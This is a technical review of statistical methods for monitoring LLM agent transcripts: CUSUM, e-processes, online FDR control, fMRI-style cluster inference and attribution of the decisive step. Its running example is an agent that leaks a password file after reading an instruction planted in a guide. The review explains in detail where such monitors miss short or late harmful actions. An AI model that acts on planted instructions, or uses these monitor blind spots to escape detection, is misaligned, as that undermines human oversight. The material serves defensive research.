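*Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* (Dubey, 2026) measured how the benefit of accumulating evidence depends on the number of steps after a failure begins. One monitor predicted each step from earlier ones and used CUSUM to accumulate the prediction errors. Another scored each step without memory. Across 1,002 runs with planted failures, including loops, repeated tool errors and drifting from the goal, the CUSUM monitor's detection rate was 9 percentage points higher than the memoryless monitor's when at most three steps followed the start of the failure, and 40 points higher when at least nine did. The monitors also differed in how they scored a step, so accumulation may not explain the whole gap.

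In a separate collection of agent runs, 61% of the failed runs ended within three steps of the first error. With a threshold set for 5% false alarms, the CUSUM monitor detected only 4.8% of the failures.

*Quickest Detection of Hallucination Onset* (Itkin, 2026) applied the delay formula to single tokens to detect where a language model's answer begins to contain unsupported statements. Each token's measurements carried about 3.5 nats of information, so the theoretical minimum delay was 1.3 tokens at one false alarm per 100 tokens. The best detectors caught fewer than a third of cases, with a delay of 11 to 13 tokens on those. Itkin attributes much of the gap to the learned score, which captured only about 22% of the available information.

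One false alarm per 100 tokens would mean 5,000 false alarms in the running example's 500,000-token transcript. At one false alarm per 500,000 tokens, the formula gives a delay of about 17 tokens for the same learned score. That is longer than the average unsupported passage in Itkin's data, which lasted about 11 tokens.

### A test that allows any number of looks

CUSUM limits how often false alarms occur. An e-process limits the chance that a clean transcript ever produces one. The team starts with a value of 1 and multiplies it by an e-value for each new step. As long as each step's e-value averages at most 1 when the step is clean, whatever happened earlier, the product is a valid e-value at any step where the team chooses to stop. Ville's inequality, named after the mathematician Jean Ville, then states that

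P(the product ever reaches 1/α) ≤ α.

An alarm at 100 therefore gives a false positive rate of at most 1% for the whole transcript, however long it is and however often the team checks it.

The guarantee requires exact e-values, but teams usually have to estimate them. *E-valuator* (Sadhuka, Prinster and colleagues, 2025) tested a variant of Ville's threshold with estimated likelihood ratios, and false alarms exceeded the target on some datasets. The paper's own method keeps the estimated ratios but sets the threshold from the highest value the ratio reaches in each successful calibration run.

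### Why the test has to restart

An e-process that starts at the first step is a poor way to detect brief harm. It works like a bettor who stakes part of their money at each step on that step being harmful. Suppose the bettor stakes about 5% on a score so extreme that only one clean step in two million reaches it. A win multiplies the money by about 100,000, and every ordinary step shrinks it by about 5%, or 0.05 nats.

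After 400 clean steps, the loss is 20 nats, and the product has fallen to e^−20, or 0.000000002. If the next step is harmful and has an e-value of 100,000, the product rises to only 0.0002. This is far below the alarm threshold of 100, so there is no alarm despite very strong evidence of harm at that step. By step 612, the loss would be over 30 nats.

Shin, Ramdas and Rinaldo (2022), in *E-detectors*, solve this by starting a new e-process at every step. The monitor then either keeps the largest of them or adds them up. It doesn't have to store them all, because simple updates are enough when each process multiplies the same step e-values *L*ₜ:

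largest: *M*ₜ = *L*ₜ · max(*M*ₜ₋₁, 1)

sum: *M*ₜ = *L*ₜ · (*M*ₜ₋₁ + 1).

The first is CUSUM without the logarithm and with a slightly different reset point. The second is the Shiryaev–Roberts procedure. With either one, raising an alarm when the statistic reaches 1,000,000 gives an average run length of at least a million steps, even if the steps are not independent.

With the bet above, the harmful step raises the largest process to 100,000. The sum reaches about 2 million and crosses the threshold, because processes that started in the previous few dozen steps still have much of their value. Shin and colleagues recommend the sum when a team can't calibrate the threshold on past data, because at the same threshold it always raises the alarm at least as early as the largest process does.

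Restarting can also limit the chance of any false alarm in a transcript if each new process gets only a share of the initial dollar. With 1,000 steps and equal shares, an e-value of 100,000 at step 612 is exactly enough to reach the threshold of 100. If the length is unknown, the shares must shrink as the run continues. For example, giving the process that starts at step *t* a share of 1/(*t*(*t* + 1)) raises the e-value that step 612 might need to about 38 million. Later harm therefore takes more evidence to detect, although the evidence required, in nats, grows only logarithmically with the step number.

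### Controlling the FDR in a stream

Online FDR procedures set a threshold for each test before its p-value arrives and never revise a decision. They treat the permitted errors as a budget. In alpha-investing, which Foster and Stine proposed in 2008, every test costs some of the budget and every alarm earns some back. Ramdas, Yang and colleagues (2017), in *Online control of the false discovery rate with decaying memory*, show that many such procedures follow from one condition:

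sum of all thresholds so far / number of alarms so far ≤ target FDR.

The sum of the thresholds is roughly the most false alarms to expect. The division uses 1 when there have been no alarms.

LORD, a widely used procedure, sets the threshold of test *t* at

γₜ*W*₀ + (α − *W*₀) · Σ γₜ₋τ,

where α is the target, *W*₀ is the starting budget, and the γ values decrease and add up to 1. The sum runs over the times τ of earlier alarms, so recent alarms loosen the threshold most. In a worked example by Sargsyan with a 5% target, the threshold starts at 0.00027, rises to 0.00247 after an alarm and falls to 0.00057 on the next test.

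With a 10% target, a starting budget of 5% and Ramdas and colleagues' default γ values, the threshold shrinks quickly if nothing triggers an alarm.

| Test number, with no earlier alarm | Threshold for the p-value |
|---|---|
| 1 | 0.0025 |
| 100 | 0.00002 |
| 612 | 0.000003 |
| 10,000 | 0.00000016 |
| 1,000,000 | 0.0000000012 |

If the team applies LORD to the steps of the running example, step 612 needs a p-value about 30 times smaller than Bonferroni would require. Ramdas and colleagues call running out of budget "alpha-death" and describe the opposite problem as "piggybacking". If an attack campaign causes 200 correct alarms, the budget grows enough to allow about 20 false ones, which may all come in the quiet days afterwards.

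SAFFRON, a later procedure, saves budget by estimating how many of the tests are clean. Rebjock, Kurt and colleagues found in *Online false discovery rate control for anomaly detection in time series* (2021) that this helps mainly when more than half of the tests have real effects. When anomalies are rare, SAFFRON loses its power, as LORD does.

### Forgetting old alarms

Decaying memory reduces both problems by giving older decisions less weight. An alarm raised *k* tests ago has weight δ<sup>*k*</sup>, with δ slightly below 1. Ramdas and colleagues let the procedure stop testing when the budget runs low and restart later, but a monitor that does this would miss any harm during the pause. Rebjock and colleagues instead keep the threshold from falling below αη(1 − δ), where η is a smoothing constant.

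In their simulations, this preserved recall when as few as one observation in 10,000 was anomalous, but precision fell. Precision would also be low for agents. With α = 10%, δ = 0.99 and η = 1, the minimum threshold is 0.001, which would produce about 10,000 false alarms a day from 10 million clean steps, compared with ten harmful steps.

The procedure still meets its target, because the decaying FDR is an average at a fixed moment. At most moments there has been no recent alarm, so the share of false alarms is close to zero. BH on small daily batches can meet its target in the same way. δ would have to be 0.999999 to bring the minimum down to 0.0000001, the cut-off that pooling a day's steps required earlier. At that value, the procedure hardly differs from a fixed threshold. Rebjock and colleagues report that a fixed threshold achieves similar combinations of precision and recall, and that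 the advantage of their rules is that the user can choose the target in advance.

Dependence between p-values is another obstacle, because the proof for LORD assumes they are independent. *e-GAI* (2025) replaces p-values with e-values and sets each threshold as a fraction of the remaining budget.

### Tests on language-model agents

Few methods have been applied to agents so far, and most of those look for failed tasks instead of harm. Sadhuka and colleagues tried to predict whether an agent or reasoning model was heading for a wrong answer on six sets of questions. On one set, with a false alarm target of 40%, their method caught 78% of the failures and flagged 31% of the successful runs. Applying a threshold calibrated the same way to the raw scores caught only 36% of the failures. Targets this high make sense for saving computation on hopeless runs, but not for monitoring harm. The method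 also trains a separate classifier for each step, which would be difficult for 1,000-step transcripts with few harmful examples. They mention detecting harmful runs only as a possible future use.

*PrefixGuard* (2026) limited false alarms to 10%, and 25 of 48 versions of its monitor never raised an alert on any test run. The monitor sorted runs into a few risk levels, and in those versions successful runs reached the highest level so often that alerting only at that level would have exceeded the limit. On the most favourable benchmark, one version caught 84% of failures with a false alarm rate of 8.8%.

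*StepShield* shows why recall is a misleading measure of a live monitor for harmful actions. Its 847 pattern-matching rules flagged 86% of harmful runs, but only 23% of those flags came between the first harmful step and three steps later, about what random timing would give. Most of the others came before any harmful step. The runs averaged only about 13 steps.

Online FDR control has even less direct support. The closest examples, from Sargsyan and from Madras and colleagues, did not involve flagging steps during a live run.

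### Blocking a step or reviewing it afterwards

A monitor that blocks step 612 before it runs has only the proposed command and the text before it as evidence, while one that checks the step afterwards can also use later steps and the tool's reply, which confirms that the file arrived. *AIR* (2026) checks each completed step, halts any continuing damage, restores a safe state where it can, and adds a rule to block similar plans in future.

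Rolling an agent back can work well for ordinary failures, but it can't retrieve a file that has already been sent outside the company. Dubey rolled flagged runs back to the last step that had gathered facts and ran them again. This repaired 45% of the failures, compared with 16% for simply retrying, and raised task success from 52% to 73%.

False alarms do more harm when they block a step, because they interrupt legitimate work and may change what the agent does next. Gao points out that stopping the agent at the first alarm prevents later attempts, so a test on completed runs can't establish how well the monitor would work in practice. Dubey found that thresholds can fail badly when the agent changes. A monitor calibrated on one model raised alarms on 75% of another model's healthy runs, which would halt most work if every alarm blocked a step.

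*Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (2026) lists how to choose intervention thresholds among the field's open questions. *SafetyDrift* (2026) estimates the chance of a violation within the next few steps. A team using it can warn the agent, suggest a safer action or pause for human approval, as well as block the agent or do nothing.

The monitor can use a looser threshold if an alarm only pauses the agent. If it pauses one clean step in 1,000 for a stronger model to check, a typical 1,000-step run stops about once, perhaps for a few seconds. The company would need about 10,000 checks a day. It could pause only actions that are hard to undo, such as sending data outside the company, and review the rest afterwards. A late alarm about step 612 would still be useful if the company could replace the passwords before anyone used them.

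## Grouping flagged tokens into spans, and what brain imaging learned about it

A probe that scores every token of the running example produces 500,000 scores, and thousands of clean tokens will score fairly high by chance. Reviewers need a few passages to read, so software has to join neighbouring high-scoring tokens into spans and decide which spans are too long to be due to chance. Brain researchers have done the same with scans since the 1990s. In 2016, a large study found that their usual formulas produced false positives at far above the stated rate. The dispute that followed exposed several mistakes that would be easy to repeat with transcripts.

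### From voxels to clusters

Functional magnetic resonance imaging (fMRI) tracks changes in the oxygen level of blood, an indirect sign of brain activity. It divides the brain into small cubes called voxels. At a typical size of 3 mm, a whole brain has about 50,000 of them, according to Stelzer, Lohmann and colleagues (2014), in *Deficient approaches to human neuroimaging*. A typical study compares two conditions, such as hearing grammatical and ungrammatical sentences, and looks for voxels whose signal differs between them. Cluster inference does this in four steps:

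1. Calculate a score for every voxel.
2. Keep the voxels that pass a first threshold, such as a p-value of 0.01 or 0.001.
3. Join neighbouring voxels into clusters.
4. Report each cluster that is larger than chance would produce.

The last step usually controls the family-wise error rate, which is the chance of at least one false alarm anywhere in the brain. If 5% of images without a real effect contain a cluster of 200 voxels or more, researchers who report only clusters of at least that size keep that chance at 5%.

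Clusters help because real effects tend to cover many neighbouring voxels. The effect in each voxel may be too weak to pass a correction for 50,000 tests, even when the group is clearly too large to have arisen by chance. The same four steps work for tokens, whose neighbours are the tokens before and after. Unlike the scan statistic described earlier, which uses windows of set lengths, cluster inference sets each span's length from the scores.

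Working out how large clusters become by chance is difficult because their size depends on how closely neighbouring scores follow each other. With a first threshold of 0.01, about 5,000 clean tokens in the running example would pass. If tokens were independent, only 0.5% of clean transcripts would contain four passing tokens in a row. If instead each passing token were followed by another half the time, a clean transcript would contain about 310 runs of four or more, and a 5% false positive rate would require a cut-off of 17 tokens.

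### A salmon in the scanner

The best-known warning about false positives in brain imaging is *Neural correlates of interspecies perspective taking in the post-mortem Atlantic Salmon* (Bennett, Baird and colleagues, 2009), in which researchers scanned a dead salmon while showing it photographs of people in social situations and asking it what the people were feeling. Of 8,064 voxels, 16 passed a threshold of 0.001, including a cluster in the brain cavity. Chance alone would produce about eight. When the researchers corrected for the number of tests, no voxels remained, even with a permitted error rate of 25%.

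The uncorrected analysis had required at least three neighbouring voxels. In an article with the same title, Bennett and colleagues argue that such minimum sizes do not replace a correction. Researchers used the same rules of thumb whether they tested 15,000 voxels or 45,000, and the resulting error rate was unknown. A rule such as "flag any five suspicious tokens in a row" would have the same weakness, because its false positive rate would depend on the transcript's length and content.

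### Three million analyses of people at rest

The salmon study showed the danger of making no correction. Eklund, Nichols and Knutsson (2016), in *Cluster failure*, tested whether the usual corrections for clusters work. They took scans of 499 healthy people at rest and analysed them as though the people had been doing a task, using invented timings. They then drew random groups and looked for activity shared by a whole group or for differences between two groups. Neither should exist, so they counted every significant cluster as a false positive.

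They ran about 3 million group analyses with the three most common software packages, SPM, FSL and AFNI. The packages' formulas were supposed to give a false positive in 5% of analyses. The table combines the study's findings with the typical ranges read from its results by Cox, Chen and colleagues in *FMRI Clustering and False Positive Rates* (2017). The rule-of-thumb figure comes from an earlier version of the study, *Can parametric statistical methods be trusted for fMRI based group studies?* (2015).

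| Method | Analyses with at least one false positive |
|---|---|
| Corrected test of each voxel | 5% or less |
| Cluster test, first threshold 0.001 | mostly 5% to 15% |
| Cluster test, first threshold 0.01 | mostly 20% to 40%, at worst 70% |
| Rule of thumb: about ten neighbouring voxels above 0.001 | mostly 50% to 90% |
| Permutation test of two groups | about 5% |

The difference between the two first thresholds is the most useful result for designing a monitor. The cluster tests adjust the required cluster size to the first threshold, so in theory either threshold should give a 5% false positive rate.

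### Why the formulas failed

The formulas assumed that the correlation between two voxels falls with distance along a bell-shaped curve, which drops almost to zero fairly quickly. In the real scans, the correlation matched this curve at short distances but was higher at long ones. This mismatch matters more with a loose first threshold than with a strict one, because a loose threshold produces larger clusters, whose size depends more on the correlation between distant voxels.

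The formulas also assumed that scans are equally smooth everywhere, but smoothness varied across the brain. False clusters were most common where smoothness was high, especially in the posterior cingulate, a region near the midline towards the back.

Uneven correlation could cause the same problem in transcripts. Suppose a clean transcript has 2,500 runs of passing tokens. In 99% of them, each passing token has a 50% chance that the next one also passes. The other 1% occur in security logs, where the chance is 95%. An engineer who fits a single correlation to all the runs would set the cut-off at 19 tokens for a 5% false positive rate. But clean transcripts would average about ten runs of at least that length in their security logs.

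A stricter significance level does little to correct a wrong null distribution, because a wrong distribution is least accurate for the most extreme chance results. In *Cluster failure revisited*, Eklund, Knutsson and Nichols (2018) ran 18,000 more null analyses with one of the standard methods. Moving from a 5% level to a 1% level should have removed 80% of the false positives, but it removed only about 31%.

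### The replies

Flandin and Friston (2017), in *Analysis of family-wise error rates in statistical parametric mapping*, defended the formulas used in SPM. They pointed out that the formulas are approximations that hold only for high first thresholds, so failure at p = 0.01 was to be expected. As a rule of thumb, a cluster with more than one peak suggests that the threshold is too low. They repeated a two-group comparison with a first threshold of p = 0.001 and 3 mm voxels, and found acceptable error rates.

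They also objected that the study had used the same invented timing for everyone. Any real change that happened at the same moment in every scan, for example as the scanner settled after starting, could then look like shared activity. The 2018 study tested this by giving each person different random timings, and the error rates were no lower, and if anything slightly higher.

Cox and colleagues, who maintain AFNI, called the conclusions "unnecessarily alarmist" because the summary gave the worst false positive rate, 70%, instead of a typical one. That rate came from a single combination of settings in FSL. In *Reply to Cox et al. and Kessler et al.* (2017), Eklund, Nichols and Knutsson accepted that quoting the highest figure had given too pessimistic a view. Both sides also agreed that a 15-year-old programming error in AFNI, which many news reports had blamed, had only a small effect. In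 one test, fixing it lowered the false positive rate from 31.0% to 27.1%.

Before comparing people, software usually converts their scans to a standard grid, and the fineness of that grid also affects the p-values of clusters. In a commentary on the study, Mueller, Lepsien and colleagues (2017) reported that when they converted the same 47 scans to finer grids in SPM, these p-values fell on average to less than half their original size. A finer grid adds no information, so a researcher could make a result significant just by changing this setting.

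Cox and Taylor (2017), in *Stability of Spatial Smoothness and Cluster-Size Threshold Estimates in FMRI using AFNI*, found no such problem in AFNI. Its smoothness estimate rose by about 0.4 mm between grids of 3 mm and 1 mm, while SPM's had fallen by about 1.6 mm. Tokens are a similarly arbitrary unit, because different language models split the same text differently. A team that replaces its probe's underlying model therefore needs a new cut-off for span length, even if the transcripts stay the same.

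### How many papers were affected

The original article referred to about 40,000 fMRI studies, and many readers thought all of them were in doubt. Nichols and his coauthors published a correction, and he wrote in the NISOx blog's *Errata for Cluster failure* (2016) that he regretted the number. He estimated that about 15,000 papers had used corrected cluster tests and that about 3,500 of these had a first threshold of 0.01 or looser. The 2018 study revised the 3,500 estimate to about 2,500 out of 23,000 fMRI publications.

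An affected paper may still be right, because a very large cluster would stay significant under a correct test. *Which Findings from the Functional Neuroimaging Literature Can We Trust?* (2016) reanalysed the real task data that Eklund and colleagues had used and controlled the false discovery rate instead of the family-wise error rate. Most of the clusters originally reported as significant passed. Nichols was more worried about another 13,000 or so papers that, by his estimate, had not corrected for multiple tests.

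Researchers were slow to change their practice. *An Updated Survey on Statistical Thresholding and Sample Size of fMRI Studies* (Yeung, 2018) reviewed 388 papers published in 2017, of which 270 used cluster tests. Of those 270, 53% used a first threshold looser than 0.001 or didn't report one. The software's default appears to have had a strong influence. The default is 0.001 in SPM and 0.01 in FSL, and about 71% of papers using SPM met the 0.001 standard, compared with 23% of those using FSL. If a monitoring tool comes with a loose default, most of its users will probably keep it.

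### Permutation tests

A permutation test avoids the formulas by using the scans to find out how large chance clusters become. To compare two groups of ten people, a researcher runs the analysis and notes the size of the largest cluster. The researcher then repeats this several thousand times, shuffling the group labels each time. If the groups don't really differ, the true labels are no more likely than the shuffled ones to produce an unusually large cluster. The largest cluster from the true labels is significant at the 5% level if at most 5% of all the arrangements, including the true one, produce a cluster at least that large.

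Shuffling moves whole scans, so it preserves the correlations inside each scan, whatever their shape. In the resting data, the two-group permutation test gave about 5% false positives with either first threshold. The choice of method can also change conclusions about real tasks. In one dataset on word and object processing, a cluster had a p-value of 0.018 by the formula and 0.249 by permutation.

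Permutation still requires the shuffled items to be interchangeable. With only one group, there are no labels to shuffle, so researchers randomly reverse the signs of people's results. This works if the noise is symmetric around zero. In some of the resting data it was not, and Cox and colleagues noted false positive rates as high as 40%. The 2018 study traced much of the problem to signals that did not come from brain activity, including those from a large vein that lies in the same place in everyone's head. After the researchers removed these signals and tested for both increases and decreases, the rates fell to about 5%.

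For transcripts, the main question is what to shuffle. Shuffling individual tokens would break up the natural runs of high scores, so almost every real transcript would look suspicious by comparison. Shuffling whole steps would preserve runs within a step but separate the twelve steps of an agent that keeps retrying an odd command. Exchanging whole transcripts preserves runs both within and across steps. To do this, the team ranks the new transcript's longest span among the longest spans of clean transcripts, which gives a conformal p-value like those in the section on calibration.

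### The cost in missed effects

Flandin and Friston argue that a test based on a correct model is at least as good at detecting real effects as any permutation test. This follows from the Neyman–Pearson lemma, a theorem about the most powerful test at a given false positive rate. They add that permutation tests take more computation, give slightly different p-values each time they are run, and are hard to apply to complicated study designs.

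The argument about power depends on having the right model. With a wrong one, the formula may detect more real effects only because its actual false positive rate is higher than stated. In the earlier example with correlated tokens, the correct cut-off of 17 would miss a harmful run of ten tokens, while the cut-off of four, which assumes independence, would catch it along with about 310 false spans. An engineer who wants to catch shorter runs would do better to choose a higher stated false positive rate than to use a wrong null distribution.

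A strict threshold also hides useful information. In *Go Figure*, Taylor, Aggarwal and colleagues (2025) show a brain image in which only one cluster, on the right side, passes the threshold. When they fade the weaker results instead of deleting them, similar activity appears on the left. They also construct four very different patterns, one of them probably an artefact, that look identical once everything below the threshold is removed.

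A monitoring tool could follow their advice by outlining the significant spans and shading the rest of the transcript by score. If one of three $3,100 payments passes the threshold and the other two fall just short, the reviewer would still see all three.

### Signal somewhere in the span

A significant cluster is evidence of a real effect somewhere inside it, but doesn't establish that every voxel is active, or which ones are. Yeung repeats this point from an earlier paper by Woo and colleagues and notes that cluster tests therefore locate effects less precisely than tests of single voxels. Larger clusters locate effects even less precisely, which is another disadvantage of a loose first threshold.

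In the running example, a monitor might flag steps 611 to 613 as one span. The statistical test supports the claim that the span contains something unusual, but not that the agent acted suspiciously in all three steps. Steps 611 and 613 only run the test suite.

The edges of a span are no more reliable. Suppose an engineer averages the scores over a sliding window of 200 tokens. In the scan example, where each harmful token's score is raised by 0.5 standard deviations, the smoothed score peaks at about 7.1 standard deviations of the smoothed noise and falls gradually as the window moves away in either direction.

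| First threshold, in standard deviations | Average length of the resulting span |
|---|---|
| 2.33 (p = 0.01) | about 270 tokens |
| 3.09 (p = 0.001) | about 225 tokens |
| 4.00 | about 175 tokens |

The harmful passage is the same in every row, and random noise would move the span's edges further. An investigator therefore can't use the first token of a span to tell when the agent began doing harm. Stelzer and colleagues describe the same effect in brain scans, where smoothing can make voxels appear active even though they contain no nerve cells. With a common setting, over 90% of a voxel's smoothed signal comes from its neighbours.

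Probes can also distort scores because a token's activations reflect earlier tokens. A password in a command may raise the scores of harmless text after it, but it can raise the scores of text before it only through the engineer's smoothing.

All-resolutions inference goes further and puts a lower limit on how much of a span is real signal. In a simple version, suppose 95% of clean transcripts have at most 30 tokens that score above 4, and a new transcript has a span with 50 such tokens. If the harmless tokens in the new transcript behave like those in clean ones, the team can be 95% confident that at most 30 of the high scores are accidental, so at least 20 of the 50 come from something real.

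The limit of 30 applies to the whole transcript, so the calculation is valid for every span at once, including one an investigator picks after looking at the scores. It doesn't identify which 20 tokens are real, and for a span with only 25 high-scoring tokens it gives a lower limit of zero. The full method combines many thresholds instead of using one. *Permutation-based true discovery proportions for functional Magnetic Resonance Imaging cluster analysis* (2020) tested two versions on resting scans. The version based on formulas gave no false positives in most settings, which suggests it was stricter than necessary. The permutation version had a false positive rate close to the intended one.

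### Measuring an effect on the data that selected it

Another mistake is to choose a region for its high scores and then use the same scores to measure the strength of the effect. For example, researchers might select the voxels whose activity correlates best with a personality test and report their average correlation. That average will be too high, because the selection favours voxels in which noise happened to increase the correlation. This error is often called circular analysis or double dipping. Bennett and colleagues credit 2009 work by Vul and colleagues and by Kriegeskorte and colleagues with drawing attention to it.

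Even after we correct for multiple tests, a real effect will look too large. Suppose clean steps score 0 on average and harmful steps score 2, both with a standard deviation of 1. If a monitor flags every step above 3, the flagged harmful steps average 3.5 and the flagged clean steps average 3.3. Reporting that a flagged step scored 3.5 therefore adds almost no information beyond the flag itself.

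The usual remedy is to select the region with one half of the data and measure the effect with the other half. Developers evaluating a monitor can likewise choose the smoothing, the first threshold and the minimum length on some transcripts and measure recall on others. Recall measured on the transcripts used to make those choices will probably be too high.

A single flagged step has no held-out half of the data to check it against, and rerunning the same monitor only reassesses the same evidence. A different kind of monitor, or a person who reads the step without seeing the score, provides better evidence.

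### A procedure for transcripts

These lessons lead to a procedure that needs no formula for the correlation between tokens:

1. Choose the monitor, the smoothing, the first threshold and the way to measure a span's size. Keep the transcripts used for these choices out of the later steps.
2. Run the entire pipeline on complete clean transcripts that resemble the new ones in length and type of work. Record the size of the largest span in each.
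3. Use these sizes to set the cut-off.
4. Run exactly the same pipeline on new transcripts and flag every span above the cut-off.

AFNI uses a similar method for brain scans. Cox and Taylor describe how it simulates 10,000 images of pure noise, records the largest cluster in each and takes the 500th largest as the cut-off for a 5% false positive rate. This cut-off is only as accurate as the simulation's model of the noise. With clean transcripts, the team doesn't need a simulation, because it can record the largest span in each transcript and set the cut-off in the same way.

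The pipeline needs a way to connect high-scoring tokens that aren't adjacent. Suppose the 200 harmful tokens score on average 3 standard deviations higher than clean ones, with independent noise. At a first threshold of 0.001, about 93 of them would pass, but the longest unbroken run would be only about six tokens. An engineer can smooth the scores first or allow spans to bridge short gaps. Both options lengthen the spans in clean transcripts, so the calibration has to include the same smoothing or bridging.

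The first threshold has to stay fixed for a similar reason. If an engineer tries both 0.01 and 0.001 on a new transcript and keeps whichever produces a significant span, the false positive rate could nearly double. Yeung found a few papers with unusual thresholds such as 0.0125 and warned that readers might think the researchers had adjusted them to get the clusters they wanted. A team that wants to use two thresholds can also run both on every clean transcript and calibrate the smaller of the two p-values.

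It also helps to record where the false spans occur, as Eklund and colleagues did for the brain. If most come from security logs or long file listings, the team can calibrate those kinds of text separately. This would lower the cut-off for the rest of the transcript, so the team could detect shorter harmful spans there.

The wording of an alert should match what the test measures. "This transcript contains a longer suspicious span than 99% of clean transcripts" is accurate. "The agent behaved harmfully from token 305,100 to token 305,370" goes beyond the evidence, because the test doesn't establish that the agent behaved harmfully or that any harmful behavior spanned exactly those tokens.

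### Where transcripts differ from brain scans

A reviewer can check a flagged span by reading it. Brain imaging researchers, according to the 2018 study, can never know for certain whether an effect in the brain is real, and they usually can't reanalyse old studies because the data are unavailable, so they depend heavily on the test's error rate. In the running example, a person can open the flagged passage and confirm within minutes that the agent copied a file of live passwords to an outside machine. Being able to check alerts this quickly reduces the harm from false positives and lets the team see whether its alerts are as reliable as the calibration implied.

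Transcripts also can't be aligned by position the way brain scans can. Brain researchers align everyone's scan to a standard template, so they can combine the same location across 20 or 40 people and detect an effect too weak to see in one person. Token 305,000 in one transcript doesn't correspond to token 305,000 in another, so a monitor has to find the harm in each transcript separately, without the gain from averaging over a group. Errors can still recur across transcripts that share content, even if it appears at different positions. If many agents open the same guide to password security, it may raise the scores in all of their transcripts, much as the vein did in the scans.

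The most important difference for the running example is that harm may be very short. A test of cluster size relies on real effects being broad, and Stelzer and colleagues warn that smoothing can hide small ones entirely. If the cut-off is 60 tokens and only the 20 tokens of a copy command score high, the test will miss the command, however high those tokens score. Adding up the scores in a span instead of counting its tokens would help, as would a separate test of the highest score with its own share of the permitted false positives.

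If a monitor scores whole steps, grouping doesn't help detect step 612. The harmful step would form a cluster of one, and at a first threshold of 0.01, about ten of the 999 clean steps would also pass. Grouping helps more when an agent does harm over several consecutive steps, for instance by deleting a company's backups one after another.

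## Finding the step that decided the outcome

A reviewer who opens a flagged span can see that the agent copied a password file. To prevent another leak, the company also has to find out why.

### Suspicious steps and decisive steps

A step is decisive if changing it would change the result. The result may be the monitor's verdict or the outcome of the run, and these can have different decisive steps. In the running example, the monitor flags the transcript because of the copy command in step 612, so deleting that step would clear the transcript. But the decisive step for the leak may be step 340, where the agent read the guide's harmless-looking sentence about copying the settings file.

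A step can also look suspicious without being decisive. Suppose the agent printed the password file at step 200 and never used the output. A monitor might give that step as high a suspicion score as step 612, but removing step 200 would not have prevented the leak.

For *TRAJDEBUG*, Qi, Yin and colleagues (2026) had annotators mark every error in 50 failed agent runs. The annotators found 381, nearly eight per run, but only one in each run counted as the cause of the failure. The agents later repaired 62% of the other errors. Another 7% had no effect, as when an agent miscounted four search results as two and never used the count.

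The usual definition of the cause comes from *Which Agent Causes Task Failures and When?* (Zhang, Yin and colleagues, 2025), which defines the decisive error as the earliest mistake whose correction would turn a failed run into a successful one. "Earliest" matters because blocking step 612 itself would also have prevented the leak. However, this definition covers only mistakes by agents, so it excludes the sentence in step 340, which is part of a tool result. The benchmark in *Long-Horizon Agent Trajectory Attribution* (Chen, Sun and colleagues, 2026) also allows tool results as causes. In its illustration, an agent makes an unsafe tool call because of an instruction planted in an earlier result.

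### Attention and gradients

Attribution methods score each part of the context by its influence on a piece of generated text, such as the command in step 612 or the monitor's verdict. The method that takes the least compute averages the model's attention to each part over all heads. A gradient method calculates how much a slight change in the numbers representing an earlier token would change the log probability of the generated text. This requires a backward pass, which takes extra time and memory.

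Average attention is unreliable, for the reasons given in the section on dilution. In *ContextCite* (described below), it came close to the best method for Llama 3 8B but did poorly for Phi-3-mini. An investigator can't tell from the scores alone which case applies.

### Removing parts of the context

A more direct test removes a step and measures how much less likely the generated text becomes. Leave-one-out repeats this for every step. For the monitor's verdict on the running example, that would take 1,000 readings of almost 500,000 tokens each, or about 500 million tokens.

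Cohen-Wang, Shah and colleagues (2024), in *ContextCite*, reduced the number of readings by removing many parts at once:

1. Delete each part of the context with a probability of 50%.
2. Calculate the probability that the model would still generate the same text.
3. Repeat this with new random deletions, 32 times in the cheapest version.
4. Fit a linear model that predicts the result from which parts remained.

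Each part's score is its weight in the linear model. The model predicts log-odds, so a weight of 2.2 means that removing the step should lower the probability of a command from, for example, 90% to 50%. The fitting method sets most weights to zero, because a statement usually depends on only a few parts of the context.

The number of deletions needed grows with the number of parts that matter multiplied by the logarithm of the total number of parts. One example in the paper used 32 deletions for 98 sentences. By that rule, 1,000 steps would take about 48 deletions if no more parts mattered than in that example. Each shortened transcript would have about 250,000 tokens, for a total of 12 million instead of 500 million.

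The linear model can fail when several parts contain the same information. If either of two sentences is enough to produce the command, leave-one-out scores both zero. Random deletion does better because it removes the other sentence half the time, so each gets about half of the full effect. With ten copies, however, each matters only when the other nine are missing, so its score falls to 0.2% of the full effect. Cohen-Wang and colleagues suggest testing the linear model on a few deletions it was not fitted to.

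Indirect influence is a bigger problem for agent transcripts. If the agent wrote "the guide says to copy the settings file" just before step 612, deleting step 340 may hardly change the probability of the command, because the agent's note still contains the instruction. The method keeps all later text fixed, so it can't detect that the agent wouldn't have written the note without the guide.

### Learning which attention heads to trust

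*Learning to Attribute with Attention* (Cohen-Wang, Chuang and Madry, April 2025) combines the two approaches in a method called Attribution with Attention (AT2). AT2 learns a weight for each attention head so that the weighted attention predicts the effect of removing parts of the context. Heads that attend to relevant text get large weights, and the others get weights near zero.

Training AT2 used 2,000 examples with 32 deletions each, or about 64,000 forward passes (single runs of the model on a text). Once trained, it scored a new text in less than half the time of one forward pass with Llama 3.1 8B. It performed about as well as fitting a new linear model to many deletions for every text. Including training, AT2 takes less computation than running 32 deletions per text once there are more than about 2,000 texts to score.

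The tests covered summaries, question answering and short reasoning problems, not agent transcripts of 500,000 tokens. AT2 also needs access to the model's attention, and it has the same problem with indirect influence because it learns from the same kind of deletion. These methods are therefore better suited to explaining a monitor's verdict, which depends on one fixed text, than to explaining what an agent did over hundreds of steps.

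### Rerunning the agent from an earlier step

To learn whether step 340 led to the leak, an investigator can restore the agent's working environment to its state before that step, replace the sentence in the guide and let the agent continue. The reruns should use dummy passwords and a sandboxed copy of the test machine so they don't cause another leak.

*ReplayRCA* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) used reruns to score how well language models diagnose failed office tasks. Each model named one step and a replacement action, and the original agent continued from there five times. The score was the success rate after the replacement minus the success rate when the original action was replayed at the same step. The replays serve as a placebo, which is needed because agents often succeed on a second try. When the researchers restarted runs at random steps without changing anything, 28% of the continuations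 succeeded.

In one failed run, the agent sent an incomplete email at step 43. When a complete email replaced it, all five reruns succeeded, compared with one of five for the placebo, an improvement of 80 percentage points. Another model chose step 42 and changed the amount of a refund. None of its five reruns succeeded, compared with three of five for the placebo, a loss of 60 percentage points. The placebo at step 42 probably did better because it let the agent write the email again.

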